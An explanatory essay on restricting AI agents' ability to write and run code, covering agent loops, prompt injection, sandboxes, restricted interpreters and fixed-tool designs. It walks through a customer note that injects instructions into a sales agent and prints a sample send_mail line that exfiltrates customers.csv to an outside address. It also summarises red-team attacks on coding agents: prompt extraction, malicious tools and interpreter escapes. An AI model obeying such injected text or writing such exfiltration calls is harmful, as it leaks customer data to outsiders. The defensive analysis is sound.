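# Limiting an AI agent's ability to write and run its own code

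## How an agent comes to write and run code

An AI agent is a language model that works towards a goal by repeatedly choosing an action and using the result to choose the next. Some actions are small and predictable, such as looking up an order or sending a message. Many agents can also write a program during a task and immediately run it on a computer. This makes them useful for work nobody planned for, but it also lets anyone who can influence what the model writes influence what the computer does, within the program's permissions.

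Developers have tried several ways to remove or divide an agent's ability to write and run code. Some give the agent a fixed set of operations and no way to write new ones. Others move the coding to a second agent, or make the model finish its program before it reads anything an outsider could have written. A company can also have its staff review programs in advance, or let the agent write any program and run it on a separate machine. All of these designs change the same basic mechanism, which has surprisingly few parts.

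### The agent loop

A language model only produces text. Ordinary software around it, called the harness, turns some of that text into action. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how this works in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness first assembles a prompt, the full text given to the model, from standing instructions, a list of available tools and the user's request. The model then outputs either a final answer or a request to use a tool. If the output is a tool request, the harness runs the tool, adds the result to the end of the prompt and queries the model again. This repeats until the model produces a final answer, which can take hundreds of rounds.

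In Bolin's example, the user asks Codex to add a diagram to a project's README file. The model requests the `shell` tool with the command `cat README.md`, which prints the file. The harness runs the command and appends the output to the prompt that contains the user's request. From then on, the model reads both the request and the file's contents whenever it picks its next step. The basic design requires this because models keep no memory between queries, so the harness has to resend the relevant history each time, as Valente explains in *Understanding the Architecture of Coding Agents* (2026).

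Valente also built a small research agent whose loop takes 18 lines of Python. Piet, Chow and colleagues (2026), in *Position*, a paper on agents that browse the web, get it down to fewer still. In outline:

```
until the task is finished:
    observation = latest result
    action = model(goal, history, observation)
    harness runs action
    add observation and action to history
```

Researchers call this pattern ReAct, for reasoning and acting. The model makes its choice in the third line, with the newest observation included in its input. The harness handles the fourth line. A model can output any request, but nothing happens until the harness carries it out, so any limit meant to hold even when the model misbehaves has to be enforced by the harness or the machine it runs on.

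### Tool calls and code actions

Suppose a sales manager asks an agent to chart last quarter's sales by region and email the chart to the finance director. The agent first needs a total for each region. One way to get it is a tool call, a structured request for a named function with filled-in parameters:

```json
{
  "name": "get_sales_total",
  "input": {"region": "West", "quarter": "2026-Q3"}
}
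```

Someone at the company wrote `get_sales_total` beforehand. The model supplies two values, and the harness runs the function and returns a number. Covering four regions takes four calls. The chart and the email each need a separate tool.

The other way is a code action, a program that the model writes during the task and has the harness run as its next step:

```python
totals = {}
for region in ["North", "South", "East", "West"]:
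    rows = query_database(
        "SELECT amount FROM sales "
        f"WHERE region = '{region}' AND quarter = '2026-Q3'")
    totals[region] = sum(row["amount"] for row in rows)
print(totals)
```

Here one program queries the database for every region, adds up the amounts and prints four totals. The idea of a code action as a general way for agents to act comes from *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2024). They proposed that every action an agent takes on its environment should be a piece of Python, and that the agent should receive the printed results or error messages as its next observation.

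A call to a predefined tool and a program written by the model can look alike when the model sends them. *Programmatic tool calling*, part of Anthropic's developer documentation for its Claude models, has a very similar loop over sales regions, and there the program is sent inside a tool call, as the text of a parameter named `code`. The difference is that a developer decided what `get_sales_total` would do before the task began, while the model decides what the Python program will do during the task.

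### Why developers allow it

The most obvious reasons for an agent to write code are loops and arithmetic. Anthropic's *Introducing advanced tool use on the Claude Developer Platform* gives the example of a manager who wants to know who on a team of 20 overspent a travel budget. With separate tool calls, the harness fetches 50 to 100 lines of expenses for each person, and more than 2,000 lines accumulate in the prompt. The model then has to add up the expenses by reading them, which is slow and prone to error. A short script can do the lookups and the sums, so that the model sees only the names of the two or three people who overspent.

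Some data is too large for a model's context window, the limit on how much text one query can involve. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* (the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting agents to outside systems) gives the example of a 10,000-row spreadsheet that a program filters down to five rows before the model reads any of it.

Writing code also lets an agent use existing software. Wang and colleagues point out that a model writing Python can import published packages and use ordinary error messages to fix its own mistakes. They add that a developer working with fixed tools might have to build a special tool just to imitate an if-statement. Most of the models they tested also did better with code on tasks that combined several tools. A model that can only produce text can still produce a chart if it writes the plotting code.

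The bigger attraction of letting an agent write code is probably that nobody has to write a tool for each task. Fixed tools would work well for the sales report if someone had written them, but next week the manager may want sales by product, or returns as a share of orders, and an agent with Python needs no new tool for either. Running agent-written code does add a burden that direct tool calls avoid. Anthropic acknowledges that a company doing this needs a secure place to run the code, limits on the resources it uses and some way to monitor it.

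### The sales report with no restrictions

Suppose now that the sales agent's one tool runs any Python the model writes, directly on a company server. That code can log in to the whole sales database and send mail from a company account. The sales table has a notes column that customers fill in on the order form. One customer has typed a remark about delivery times and, below it, a sentence telling any AI system preparing a report to attach the full customer list and copy the message to a specified outside address.

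The task then runs like this:

1. The harness sends the model the manager's request and a description of the Python tool.
2. The model writes a short program that prints the first 20 rows of the sales table, to learn what the columns contain and how the dates look. A human programmer would do the same. The harness runs it.
3. The harness adds the 20 rows to the prompt. The customer's note is in one of them.
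4. The model writes a second program, which totals the sales by region and draws the chart. If it crashes, the error message goes back to the model, which tries again.
5. The model writes a third program, which mails the chart, and the harness runs that too.
6. The model tells the manager that the report is on its way.

The note gets its chance between steps 3 and 4. Until then the model has written code on the strength of the manager's request and the developer's instructions alone. Afterwards it writes every program with the customer's text in view. If the model ignores the note, the mailing program in step 5 contains a line like this:

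```python
send_mail(to=["finance.director@company.example"],
          attach=["chart.png"])
```

If the model follows the note, the line becomes:

```python
send_mail(to=["finance.director@company.example",
              "reports@outsider.example"],
          attach=["chart.png", "customers.csv"])
```

No component malfunctioned in this attack. The database returned the right rows, Python ran a valid program, and the mail left from an account with permission to send it. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (May 2026) notes that logs of such an attack show only a successful, authorised call, with no sign that anything went wrong.

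Piet and colleagues compare an attacker who takes over an agent's choice of actions to one who controls the input of `eval`, the Python function that runs text as code. The comparison is an analogy for web agents that click and type, but it describes the sales agent almost literally. NVIDIA's *Sandboxing Agentic AI Workflows with WebAssembly* describes a chart-drawing agent whose application also passes the model's Python to `eval` on the server. Malicious code could compromise the application, and possibly the operating system and other users.

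If the first program had added up the amounts and printed only the totals, the note would have passed through Python without reaching the model. In Anthropic's system, too, the model receives only the program's final output. Code execution therefore sometimes keeps an outsider's text away from the model, but nothing in the unrestricted version enforces this. Here the note reached the model because the model wrote a program that printed some of the rows, and an error message quoting the row containing the note would have had the same effect.

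A model may follow orders in a customer's note even though harnesses mark where text comes from. Bolin lists four roles for the items in a prompt, from most weight to least: system, developer, user and assistant. These roles only guide how much weight the model gives each item, and it can misjudge. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a post for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, explains that a database engine can keep a query apart from the data it handles, while a language model only predicts the next token, or fragment of text, from all the text so far. Training makes models much less likely to obey such notes. Anthropic reports that attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 in one benchmark succeeded about 0.1% of the time on a single attempt and 5 to 6% of the time when the attacker had 100 attempts and could adapt. A customer can also try repeatedly by submitting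 an order form more than once, but will find it harder to adapt without seeing the agent's output.

Researchers have demonstrated attacks very similar to this one. Willison (2025) recounts a scenario from a team at General Analysis in which a developer asks the coding assistant Cursor to list recent support tickets from a Supabase database. The assistant's account bypasses the rules on who may see which rows. One ticket contains instructions to read a table of secret access tokens and post the contents as a reply, where the attacker can read them. In *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025), Supabase says that no customer had reported such a leak but accepts that the risk is real. The company had wrapped query results in warnings to the model, which reduced the problem without removing it. In a scenario from Trend Micro's *Unveiling AI Agent Vulnerabilities Part IV*, text in a customer feedback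 field makes an assistant drop the summary it was preparing and send a phishing email that looks like an internal message. Attackers are trying similar things outside research settings. Mascellino (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*, reports that the security company Zscaler found websites with hidden text meant to manipulate agents into making cryptocurrency payments.

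### Some security terms

In a prompt injection, a model follows instructions hidden in content it reads. The term dates from 2022. David C gives the example of a job applicant whose CV contains an invisible instruction for the recruiter's model to approve it for interview. Security people call this indirect prompt injection, because the attacker writes something that the AI system will later process, without interacting with it directly. The customer's note is another example.

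A confused deputy is a program that an outsider tricks into using its authority on the outsider's behalf. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* describes a compiler, a program that translates source code, which had permission to write in its own directory so that it could keep usage statistics. The company's billing file was in the same directory. A user named that file as the destination for debugging output, and the compiler overwrote the bills. The compiler held authority from two sources and could not keep them apart. The sales agent has the same problem, because its rights over the database and the mail come from the company, but an outsider can use them through the note. Programmers can repair an ordinary confused deputy, but David C argues that a language model is "inherently confusable".

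A sandbox limits which files, networks and processes a running program can reach. Web browsers run pages in one, which is why a web page cannot read the files on a visitor's computer or switch on the webcam without permission. A sandbox could keep the sales agent's Python code away from the rest of the server, but the code would still need access to the database and the mail to do its job. The altered email uses only those two, so the sandbox would not stop it.

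An attack surface is all the points where an outsider can influence what a system does. *Attack surface*, a glossary entry from NIST, the US standards institute, also counts the points where an attacker can try to get data out. An attacker could influence the sales agent through the notes column and get data out through the mail account. The column is part of the surface even if the database software is entirely trustworthy, because customers write its contents.

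Blast radius is the most damage that a failure or a successful attack could do. Anthropic distinguishes it from the likelihood of failure, and observes that better training and safeguards have reduced that likelihood while the possible damage grows with every new permission. The unrestricted sales agent's blast radius includes every record the database account can read or change, every message the mail account can send, and anything else on the server that the Python process can access. A read-only database account would reduce the blast radius, because instructions in the note could no longer cause the agent to delete records, though they could still cause it to email them out.

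## When an agent counts as running its own code, and what that exposes

The unrestricted sales agent clearly "runs its own code", but the phrase merges four questions:

1. Who writes the code?
2. Who decides that it runs?
3. Whose permissions does it run with?
4. Was the code final before a model read any untrusted content, meaning text or data that someone other than the user or developer could have written?

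A developer can change one of these and leave the rest alone. A read-only database account changes only the permissions. Making the model finish its whole program before it sees any rows changes only the timing, and the customer's note then arrives too late to alter the line that sends the mail. The main designs for limiting an agent's code compare as follows:

| Design | Who writes the code | Who decides that it runs | Whose permissions it has | Final before untrusted content arrives? |
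|---|---|---|---|---|
| Unrestricted agent | The model, during the task | The model | The company server's, including database and mail | No |
| Fixed tools | Developers | The model, by choosing a tool and its parameters | Each tool's own | The code is, but the choice of calls is not |
| Separate coding agent | A second model | The main agent asks, and the second agent has the code run | Whatever the developer gives the second agent | Only if nothing untrusted reaches the second model |
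| Program written first | The model, from the user's request | The harness, once the program is complete | The user's or company's, through approved functions | Yes |
| Code generated and reviewed in advance | A model, subject to checks or staff review | A user, a schedule or an agent that calls it as a tool | The account that staff assign to it | Yes |
| Separate machine | The model, during the task | The model | That machine's | No |

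Moving the code to a separate machine changes only its permissions. An attacker who steers the agent can still have it write any program, so the protection depends on what the machine can reach. With fixed tools, the attacker can't have the agent write a new program, but the model still chooses which tools to call after reading the attacker's note. Companies can also combine designs, such as by putting a coding agent on a separate machine.

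Researchers have built systems of the two less familiar kinds. *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* (2026) describes Baya, in which a coding agent writes and checks a Python program without access to the live website, and a separate engine then runs the program on the site. Baya treats the website's operator and the code behind the site's functions as trusted, but not the reviews, adverts and comments that third parties put there. In *Compiled AI* (2026), a model writes a piece of business software once, inside a template. The code must pass checks for security, syntax, execution and accuracy, and if it fails one, the model is given the errors and tries again. *Metadata-Driven AI* (2026) presents a similar design and notes that the approved code then runs with no further calls to a model.

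### Hard cases

The table leaves "code" undefined. An agent runs its own code when software treats text that the agent's model wrote during the task as instructions, and those instructions can express operations that no developer chose to offer. This definition covers most cases.

An agent that can write and run its own SQL queries meets this definition even if it can't run Python. If it can write any query, it can query the sales database for the customer list as easily as for regional totals. The possible damage is usually smaller than with Python. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) notes that SQL is a specialised language and that databases have their own rules about who may see what.

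**An allowed shell command with free arguments** can let an agent run its own code, even though a developer chose the command. For example, `find`, which searches for files, has an option that starts other programs. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (Hegelich, Sarhan and colleagues, 2026) lists this among the ways an approved command can turn into a full shell. If the developer blocks that option, using `find` no longer counts as the agent running its own code, but the agent still isn't necessarily safe. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an attack that needs no code, in which an injection gets an agent that can only find and move files to look for sensitive ones and put them on a public network drive.

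Whether a template with blanks lets an agent run its own code depends on how the harness fills the blanks. Suppose a developer writes a sales query and leaves a blank for the region. If the harness sends the region to the database separately from the query, the database engine can only compare it with the region names in the table. If the harness pastes the region into the text of the query, any SQL in the "region" becomes part of the query. The model supplies one piece of text either way, so it can't distinguish the two cases.

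A plan in JSON, a format for structured data, works as a program if an engine carries it out. The plan sets the control flow (which operations run and in what order) and the data flow (which values pass through them). Beurer-Kellner and colleagues therefore treat a plan in an internal format and a plan in ordinary code as versions of one design. If every step calls a function that a developer wrote, the model can rearrange those functions but can't add to them, so the agent doesn't count as running its own code. It does count if even one step runs a script the model chooses. The same test applies to a plan in Python, which would be no more dangerous than the JSON plan if it could only call the same functions.

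An agent that can send free-form requests to a coding delegate, a separate tool or agent that writes code on request, is still running its own code. The request may be in plain language and contain no code, but the delegate treats it as instructions. The main agent can therefore request operations that no developer offered, such as sending the customer list to an outside address. To prevent this, the developer has to limit what the request can contain or what the delegate will do with it.

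A settings file takes effect only when another program loads it. If the file can name a command to run, an agent allowed only to write files can use it to write code that will run later with the other program's permissions. Fadilpašić (2026), in *Top AI coding agents can be easy victims to sandbox escapes*, reports on attacks in which programs outside the sandbox act on what an agent wrote inside it.

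### A restricted Python interpreter

Researchers have done little work on the security of agents that run their own code. Hossain, Hossain and Ansari (2026), in *On Understanding, Identifying, and Mitigating Vulnerabilities in Agentic Large Language Models*, reviewed 85 papers on agent security from 2023 to 2025. Two thirds concerned attacks on what the model reads, such as prompt injection, and only three (3.5%) concerned the security of code execution.

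The security company NCC Group analysed smolagents, Hugging Face's library for building agents. Its `CodeAgent` acts by writing Python, which the library runs immediately and without review. By default, the code runs in an interpreter that works through the program piece by piece, blocks operations it doesn't recognise and stops programs that run too long. The code can import only 11 modules, for tasks such as mathematics and handling dates and text. None is intended for opening files or network connections, so a default `CodeAgent` is meant to be almost as harmless as the JSON plan.

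Williams (2025), in *Autonomous AI Agents*, looked at what happens when developers permit more modules. The popular data libraries `pandas` and `numpy` can both read and write files, a danger less obvious than that of a module that runs operating-system commands. Hugging Face's course on agents, which more than 100,000 people had joined, permitted both libraries in an example without a warning. Williams built an agent with the course's list of modules and no other tools. He asked it to print the source code of any agent it could find on the disk, using only the permitted modules, and then to create a small Python file. Both requests worked, though not every time. An attacker who could do the same could overwrite the agent's own program, which runs outside the special interpreter and has none of its limits.

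Williams typed these requests himself and gives no success rate, so his test shows what the interpreter allows once a model cooperates, but not how often a hidden note would get a model to cooperate. The sales agent is still at risk, because `pandas` is an obvious choice for adding up a quarter's sales by region, and a developer might well permit it without thinking about file access.

Allowing only the default modules would not have prevented escapes either. NVD's *CVE-2025-5120 Detail*, an entry in the US government's database of software flaws, records that attackers could use approved modules and functions to escape the interpreter in smolagents 1.14.0 and run any code on the host. GitLab lists the flaw as fixed in version 1.17.0. JFrog's *Smolagents Local Python Sandbox Escape* (2025) reported another escape in versions before 1.21.0, which attackers could exploit by tricking the agent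 into writing the malicious code.

In an older version of its documentation, *Secure code execution*, Hugging Face said it had never seen the interpreter allow any damage but called the interpreter "not watertight". For example, a program with permission to process images could save thousands of them and fill the disk. A later version, *smolagents documentation*, warns that agents that write code give the model more freedom than other designs and carry more risk. Williams recommends a container or remote machine for any production system. He also recommends that developers write a specific tool whenever an agent needs a database or the internet, and use the generated Python only for logic, arithmetic and calling those tools.

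### Coding agents with a malicious tool

In *Red-Teaming Coding Agents from a Tool-Invocation Perspective*, Xie, Luo and colleagues (2025) measured how often an outsider could get a model to comply. They attacked six products that can run commands on a programmer's computer: Cursor, Claude Code, Copilot, Windsurf, Cline and Trae. They assumed that the victim had connected the agent to an external tool controlled by the attacker, who wrote the tool's description and replies but could not change the model or directly use the agent's built-in tools. This attacker has more control than a customer with a notes field, but the scenario is plausible because the public registries where programmers find such tools do little vetting.

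The researchers first extracted the hidden instructions from their own copy of each product by adding a tool that took those instructions as a parameter. Models that would refuse a direct request for them often filled in the parameter. The researchers then used the instructions to tailor the main attack, in which a user asks the agent to write a maze game. The malicious tool's description leads the agent to call the tool first, and the tool's reply leads it to download and run a program. The researchers made up to ten attempts on each combination of product and model. They counted an attempt as successful if the agent requested the intended command, even if the command would have done no harm on a real machine.

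On the older releases, the attack succeeded at least 20% of the time with each of the 25 combinations, and about 73% of the time on average. It succeeded much less often when the researchers put the whole attack in the tool's description and nothing in its reply. They think this is because models tend to treat descriptions as reference material, while a reply, like the rows the sales agent prints, arrives just before the model chooses its next step.

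In 2026 the researchers repeated the attack on newer releases and models:

| Product | Older release, older models | Newer release, older models | Newer release, newer models |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cline | 20–100% | 30–100% | 0% (Claude Sonnet 4.6, Opus 4.7), 20% (GPT-5.5), 100% (Gemini 3.1 Pro, Grok 4.20) |
| Windsurf | 50–100% | 50–100% | 0% (Sonnet 4.6, Opus 4.7), 10% (GPT-5.5), 100% (Gemini 3.1 Pro) |
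| Trae | 20–80% | Not tested | 0% (GPT-5.5), 100% (Gemini 3.1 Pro) |
| Cursor | 40–100% | 10–20% | 30% (Gemini 3.1 Pro), 0% (four others) |
| Claude Code | 60–70% | 0% | 0% |
| Copilot | 20–100% | Not tested | Not tested |

Cursor and Claude Code improved even with the older models. Both had switched from putting full tool descriptions in the prompt to listing only the tools' names, so the first half of the attack never reached the model. Cline and Windsurf did not improve with the older models, but the attack failed every time on both when they ran Sonnet 4.6 or Opus 4.7.

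Xie and colleagues conclude that the redesign is the decisive defence and that products without it remain exposed whatever model they use. Their results don't quite support this, because the newer Claude models stopped the attack without the redesign. The results with Gemini 3.1 Pro support the conclusion better: the attack always worked on the three products without the redesign, but only 30% of the time on Cursor, which has it. The success rates of zero are also uncertain, because an attack that works a quarter of the time would still fail ten times in a row about 6% of the time.

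The agent can still run commands after both changes, so an attacker can look for another way to exploit that ability. According to the AI Now Institute's *Exploit Brief*, in 2026 an outsider could still get coding agents using Claude Sonnet 5, Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5 to run a malicious program.

### Defences that leave the ability in place

A restriction takes away an agent's ability to write and run code, while refusal training, permission prompts and output filters leave that ability in place. Training makes a model less likely to write a harmful program, a permission prompt gives a person the chance to stop the program, and an output filter inspects it automatically. A simple way to tell the difference is to suppose that the model does exactly what the attacker wants. If the sales agent has only fixed tools, the harness still has no way to run the attacker's program, but if the agent has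 Python and relies only on training, it can run the program.

Measurements of how well training works vary widely. In *INFUSE* (2026), a benchmark of hidden instructions, 19.6% of attacks succeeded on average, and GPT-5 did worse than the smaller GPT-5-Nano. *When Coding Agents Get Arms* (2026) tested coding agents that control robots, using models from the GPT-6 generation. Hidden instructions succeeded in 82 to 91% of cases, but the sample was probably small, since the exact percentages match nine and ten out of eleven. Anthropic reports that Claude Mythos 5 had the best result yet on a prompt-injection benchmark from the security company Gray Swan. The developer of the sales agent has no good way to know which of these results to expect.

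Filters can also block useful work. Hegelich and colleagues tried several on 120 attacks and 120 harmless programming actions. A list of forbidden text patterns blocked 44% of the attacks and none of the harmless actions. A small language model used as a judge blocked every attack but also 98% of the harmless actions. A larger model would probably judge better. The researchers were also promoting their own monitor, which applies fixed rules. In its first test, it blocked 94% of the attacks with no false alarms.

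A filter can detect an attack without stopping it if the harness leaves the final decision to the main model. In one of Xie and colleagues' attacks on an older release of Claude Code, a second model inspected the command and correctly labelled it an injection. The product passed this verdict to the main model as advice. The main model, already influenced by the malicious tool, dismissed the warning as a false alarm and ran the command.

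Permission prompts depend on people, who can get tired and approve something dangerous. *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* (2026) recommends several defences together, including a list of allowed tools for each task, and warns against relying on the model's training or instructions alone. Restrictions can fail too, as the smolagents interpreter did, but its developers could fix a specific flaw and release a new version, while nobody knows how to make a model ignore every hidden instruction.

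### The argument for delegation

Some developers want to keep the usefulness of generated code without letting the main agent write it, so they hand the writing to a coding delegate. The argument that this makes the system safer has four premises:

1. An agent that cannot supply executable text can do only what its tools allow.
2. Untrusted content that reaches the agent cannot determine what the delegate writes or runs.
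3. The delegate's code runs with less authority than the undivided agent had.
4. The added parts expose less than the division removes.

The argument can still hold if only one of the two protections fails. An outsider who can influence the delegate's code achieves little if that code has little authority, and can't use the code's authority without a way to influence it. If both protections fail, the company has moved the dangerous code to another component and gained almost nothing.

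The premise that an agent can do only what its tools allow is false if other software executes even one of its tool parameters. Possible examples from the hard cases include a shell option, a value pasted into a query and a settings file. Even when the premise is true, it may give little protection. If the sales agent has a mail tool that sends any file to any address, the customer's note can succeed without any code.

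Beurer-Kellner and colleagues base their designs on the stricter principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, it must be impossible for that input to trigger any consequential action. Refuting the premise about the delegate would require showing that text in the notes column can change which operations the delegate's program performs. The text could reach the delegate in the main agent's request, or in sample rows and error messages that the delegate reads. A customer who enters a false order amount can change the total for the West region, but this does not refute the premise because the program still performs the same operations. Piet and colleagues call this outcome manipulation, and distinguish it from control-flow hijacking, in which the attacker gets the agent to do things outside its task.

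*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) mathematically analyzes a closely related question for agents that fix their plan before reading anything untrusted and have a monitor that allows or denies each call. It compares such an agent with a reference agent that has the same plan and monitor, but a model that never obeys untrusted content. The real agent counts as secure if it leaks nothing that the reference agent wouldn't also leak. Suppose a user wants an assistant to send her calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting. A hidden instruction that obtains her password-reset code adds a leak, but one that obtains her calendar doesn't, because an ordinary meeting request would have obtained it too.

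Dongol gave a computer-checked proof that an agent is secure in this sense if the monitor withdraws every tool an injection could call when the agent first reads untrusted content, and never gives the tools back. If the agent instead reads an untrusted email and then a secret before it loses its mail tool, an injection can send the secret. If the monitor withdraws the tool after the email but before the secret, an injection can still send anything private that was already in memory. The proof assumes that each injection causes a single call, that secrets and the monitor's replies don't affect when the model follows an injection, and that the attacker sees the content and order of messages but not their timing.

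Besides injections that make a single call, Dongol considers ones that run a whole program and ones that corrupt the answer of a quarantined model, which reads untrusted content but has no tools and returns only data. An injected program can leak a secret without sending anything itself, by overwriting a variable that the original plan sends later. Withdrawing tools can also block legitimate work. The sales agent would lose its mail tool before the first row arrived, so it could never send the chart.

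Hegelich and colleagues apply a computer security rule from Saltzer and Schroeder (1975), that a program should have only the privileges its job requires. Coding agents usually start with far more, because they inherit access to the user's files, passwords and network. To check that a delegate has less authority than a single agent doing the whole job, a developer could list everything the delegate's code can read, change and send, and compare it with what the single agent could do. A delegate that needs sales figures may well get the same database login the single agent had, which leaves its access to the database just as broad even if it can't send mail. The comparison also has to cover what the delegate and the main agent can do together. Hegelich and colleagues warn that two agents with different permissions can leak data through a shared file without either breaking its own rules. For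 example, if the delegate can save the customer list to a folder and the main agent can mail files from that folder, together they can still send out the list, as the single agent could.

Adding a delegate gives attackers more parts to target. The system needs messages between the agents and often an orchestrator, the agent or program that decides which of them acts next. Hossain and colleagues note that systems with several agents give attackers a new route, because an outsider can inject messages or impersonate an agent. The delegate may also bring its own packages and plugins. Constantin (2026), in *Plugin4Shell*, reports a flaw in the plugin systems of Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI that let the owner of a code repository replace an approved plugin with a malicious one without the user clicking anything. Saltzer and Schroeder also advised keeping protection mechanisms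 small, because errors in them go unnoticed in normal use.

This last premise would be false if an attack through one of the new parts were as easy and as damaging as the attack on the undivided agent. It is probably the hardest premise to test, because there is no agreed unit for how much a system exposes. A fair comparison would include the same attacks on both versions of the sales agent, plus attacks on the messages, the orchestrator and the delegate's plugins. Using only the old attacks would make the divided agent look safer than it is.

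## Replacing code with a fixed set of actions

The strictest design removes the Python tool and gives the model a short list of actions that developers wrote beforehand. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues call this the action-selector pattern and compare the model to a switch statement, the part of a program that picks one of several prepared branches. One of their examples is a customer service chatbot that can do little more than fetch a link to the customer's last order or point to the settings page for changing a password.

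### Two tools for the sales agent

The sales report needs only two tools:

```
make_sales_chart(region, quarter, chart_type)
email_chart(chart, recipient)
```

The developers list every value that the model may fill in:

| Parameter | Permitted values | Number |
|---|---|---|
| `region` | North, South, East, West, or all four on one chart | 5 |
| `quarter` | The last eight quarters | 8 |
| `chart_type` | Bar, line, pie | 3 |
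| `recipient` | The finance director, four regional managers, the outside auditor | 6 |

The task then runs like this:

1. The manager asks for last quarter's sales by region, sent to the finance director.
2. The harness sends the model this request and the descriptions of the two tools, but no sales data.
3. The model replies with both calls filled in: all regions, third quarter of 2026, bar chart, finance director.
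4. The harness checks each value against its list and refuses the calls if any value isn't there.
5. The harness runs the two functions. The developers' code queries the database, draws the chart, looks up the finance director's address and sends the mail.
6. The harness tells the manager, in a fixed sentence, that the chart has gone out. The model sees neither the rows nor the result.

The customer's note stays in the database and the model never reads it, so it doesn't matter how the model would have reacted to it.

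There are 5 × 8 × 3 = 120 possible charts and six possible recipients, which makes 720 possible emails. The agent with Python has no fixed number of possible actions, because the model can write a program of any length. A developer could list all 720 emails and look for any that would cause trouble, such as the North manager receiving West's figures.

The pattern doesn't protect against text in the request itself. If the manager pastes in a customer's email, the customer's words reach the model in step 2 and can affect which of the 720 it picks. The design also prevents the model from detecting a blank chart, and it can't handle a request like "copy in the West manager if West's sales fell", because that information never reaches the model.

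### When results go back to the model

Most agents with fixed tools are less strict than this and let the model see each result before it chooses its next call. Some designs make the model commit to its whole list of calls before it sees any result. Suppose `make_sales_chart` also returns the regional totals and, to help explain unusual figures, the customer's note on the largest order. A customer who places a big enough order can then write text in the note that the model will read just before it calls `email_chart`.

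This attacker still can't get the customer list, because neither tool can send it, and can't make the agent send anything to an outside address they choose. But they could make the agent send the finance director a chart for the wrong quarter, or send West's figures to the auditor. They could also make it tell the manager that it sent an email when it sent nothing. The agent's closing message is free text, so it could contain a false total or a link to a malicious site. The 720 counts different emails, and the agent can send the same one repeatedly, so an attacker could flood the finance director's inbox unless the harness limits the number of calls.

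An attacker who can read one recipient's mail could use the choice of chart as a code. With 120 charts to choose from, eight emails are enough to encode a 16-digit card number. But the model would first have to see a card number, and these two tools never give it one.

### Harmless commands that combine into harm

The argument for delegation rests on the premise that an agent that can't supply executable text can do only what its tools allow. This is true of the two sales tools, and they allow so little that the restriction gives real protection. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues analyse a case in which the tools allow far more, an operating-system assistant that organises files on request. For example, it might move all tax-related PDFs into a folder called Taxes, or identify the songs in a music folder and rename the files. The attacker controls the names or contents of some of the files.

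If an assistant has a full shell, any file it reads could lead it to run arbitrary code. Even without an attacker, it might delete many files by mistake. Asking the user to confirm each command is tedious and probably doesn't help much, because many users can't judge shell commands and an attacker can make a harmful one look innocent. An action selector, which limits the model to choosing from hard-coded commands, is immune to malicious files because the model never reads them. But it also can't do tasks that depend on what files contain, such as finding the PDFs about tax, which was the reason for using a model.

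In an intermediate design, the assistant commits in advance to the few commands a task needs, such as `find` and `mv` (which moves files) for sorting a Downloads folder. The model still decides what to search for and where to move it, so the attack mentioned earlier works here. An injection can get sensitive files moved to a public network drive even though the premise about executable text holds throughout.

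This agent differs from the sales agent in the range of values its parameters accept. The sales agent's `recipient` accepts six values, while `mv` accepts any path on the system, including the public drive. If the developer allowed only folders on the user's own desktop as destinations, this attack would fail even though the agent kept the same two commands. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues prefer to have a separate quarantined model read each file and return only yes or no, or a category from a list. A controller then moves the files based on these answers, without reading any contents. A malicious file can still end up in the wrong folder, but it can't affect how the other files are handled.

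### A coding agent with a fixed test command

Valente's research agent, Ark, programs using five fixed tools, compared with more than 20 tools in Codex. Ark's tools list files, read a file, search for text, run the project's tests, and end the task by proposing a patch (a set of changes to the files). The test tool always runs `pytest`, a standard testing program for Python, and the model can't change the command. The file tools work only inside a temporary copy of the project, and Ark shows the user each patch and asks for approval before applying it.

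Ark, using GPT-5.4 mini, completed eight of ten small maintenance tasks, with one attempt at each, for less than 50 cents in total. In one failure, it fixed a bug only for the cases the visible tests covered. In the other, it renamed a function without updating every file that used the old name. Neither failure obviously came from the lack of a shell.

Ark can run its own code, although it seems unable to. On every task it applied the patch and then ran the tests with `pytest`, which runs the project's code, including whatever the model has just written. Ark's path checks apply to its file tools, not to programs that `pytest` starts, and Ark runs commands directly on the user's machine without a sandbox. An instruction hidden in a source file could therefore get the model to add a line that uploads the user's passwords, and the fixed `pytest` command would run it. The only safeguard is the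 user reading the patch before approving it.

The premise fails here because one of the tool's parameters is the text of a patch, which other software then executes. A coding agent can hardly test its own work without this, so even a fixed command needs a sandbox.

### Which coding tools enforce a tool list

Someone who builds a harness for the sales agent can leave out the Python tool. Someone using an existing coding product has to switch tools off, usually by listing the permitted ones in a configuration file. Like any other limit, the list can stop an attacker only if the harness enforces it.

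Madatha (2026), in *A Deterministic Control Plane for LLM Coding Agents*, compared how products treated such lists in June 2026:

| Product | Enforcement of the declared list at run time |
|---|---|
| Claude Code | Reads the list when a session starts and rejects calls to other tools. It can also run a check before each tool call. |
| Cursor | Partial. Rules and server settings limit tools indirectly, and a check can block shell commands, but nothing compares calls with the agent's list. |
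| Copilot in VS Code | None from the configuration file, although the file has a field for the list. |
| Aider | None from the configuration file, and the agent has shell access. |
| Codex, Windsurf, OpenCode, Kiro | Little or none. |

These products change quickly, and Madatha was presenting a system that adds the missing checks, so a developer should test the current version before relying on a list. A product in the bottom row may have other protections. For example, Codex has a sandbox that limits what a command can reach, but not which tools the model can call.

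Few people seem to use these lists. Madatha searched 6,145 configuration files for coding agents in public repositories and found that only 31, about 0.5%, declared permissions. A third of the files for GitHub Actions, a service that runs automated jobs on code, declared them. The gap is large, although the search could easily have missed some declarations because the products have no standard format for them.

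### The cost in task success

An agent with fixed tools fails completely at a task it has no tool for. Benchmarks rarely measure this, because they supply the tools each task needs. They usually measure whether a model does better by calling those tools one at a time or by writing a program that calls them.

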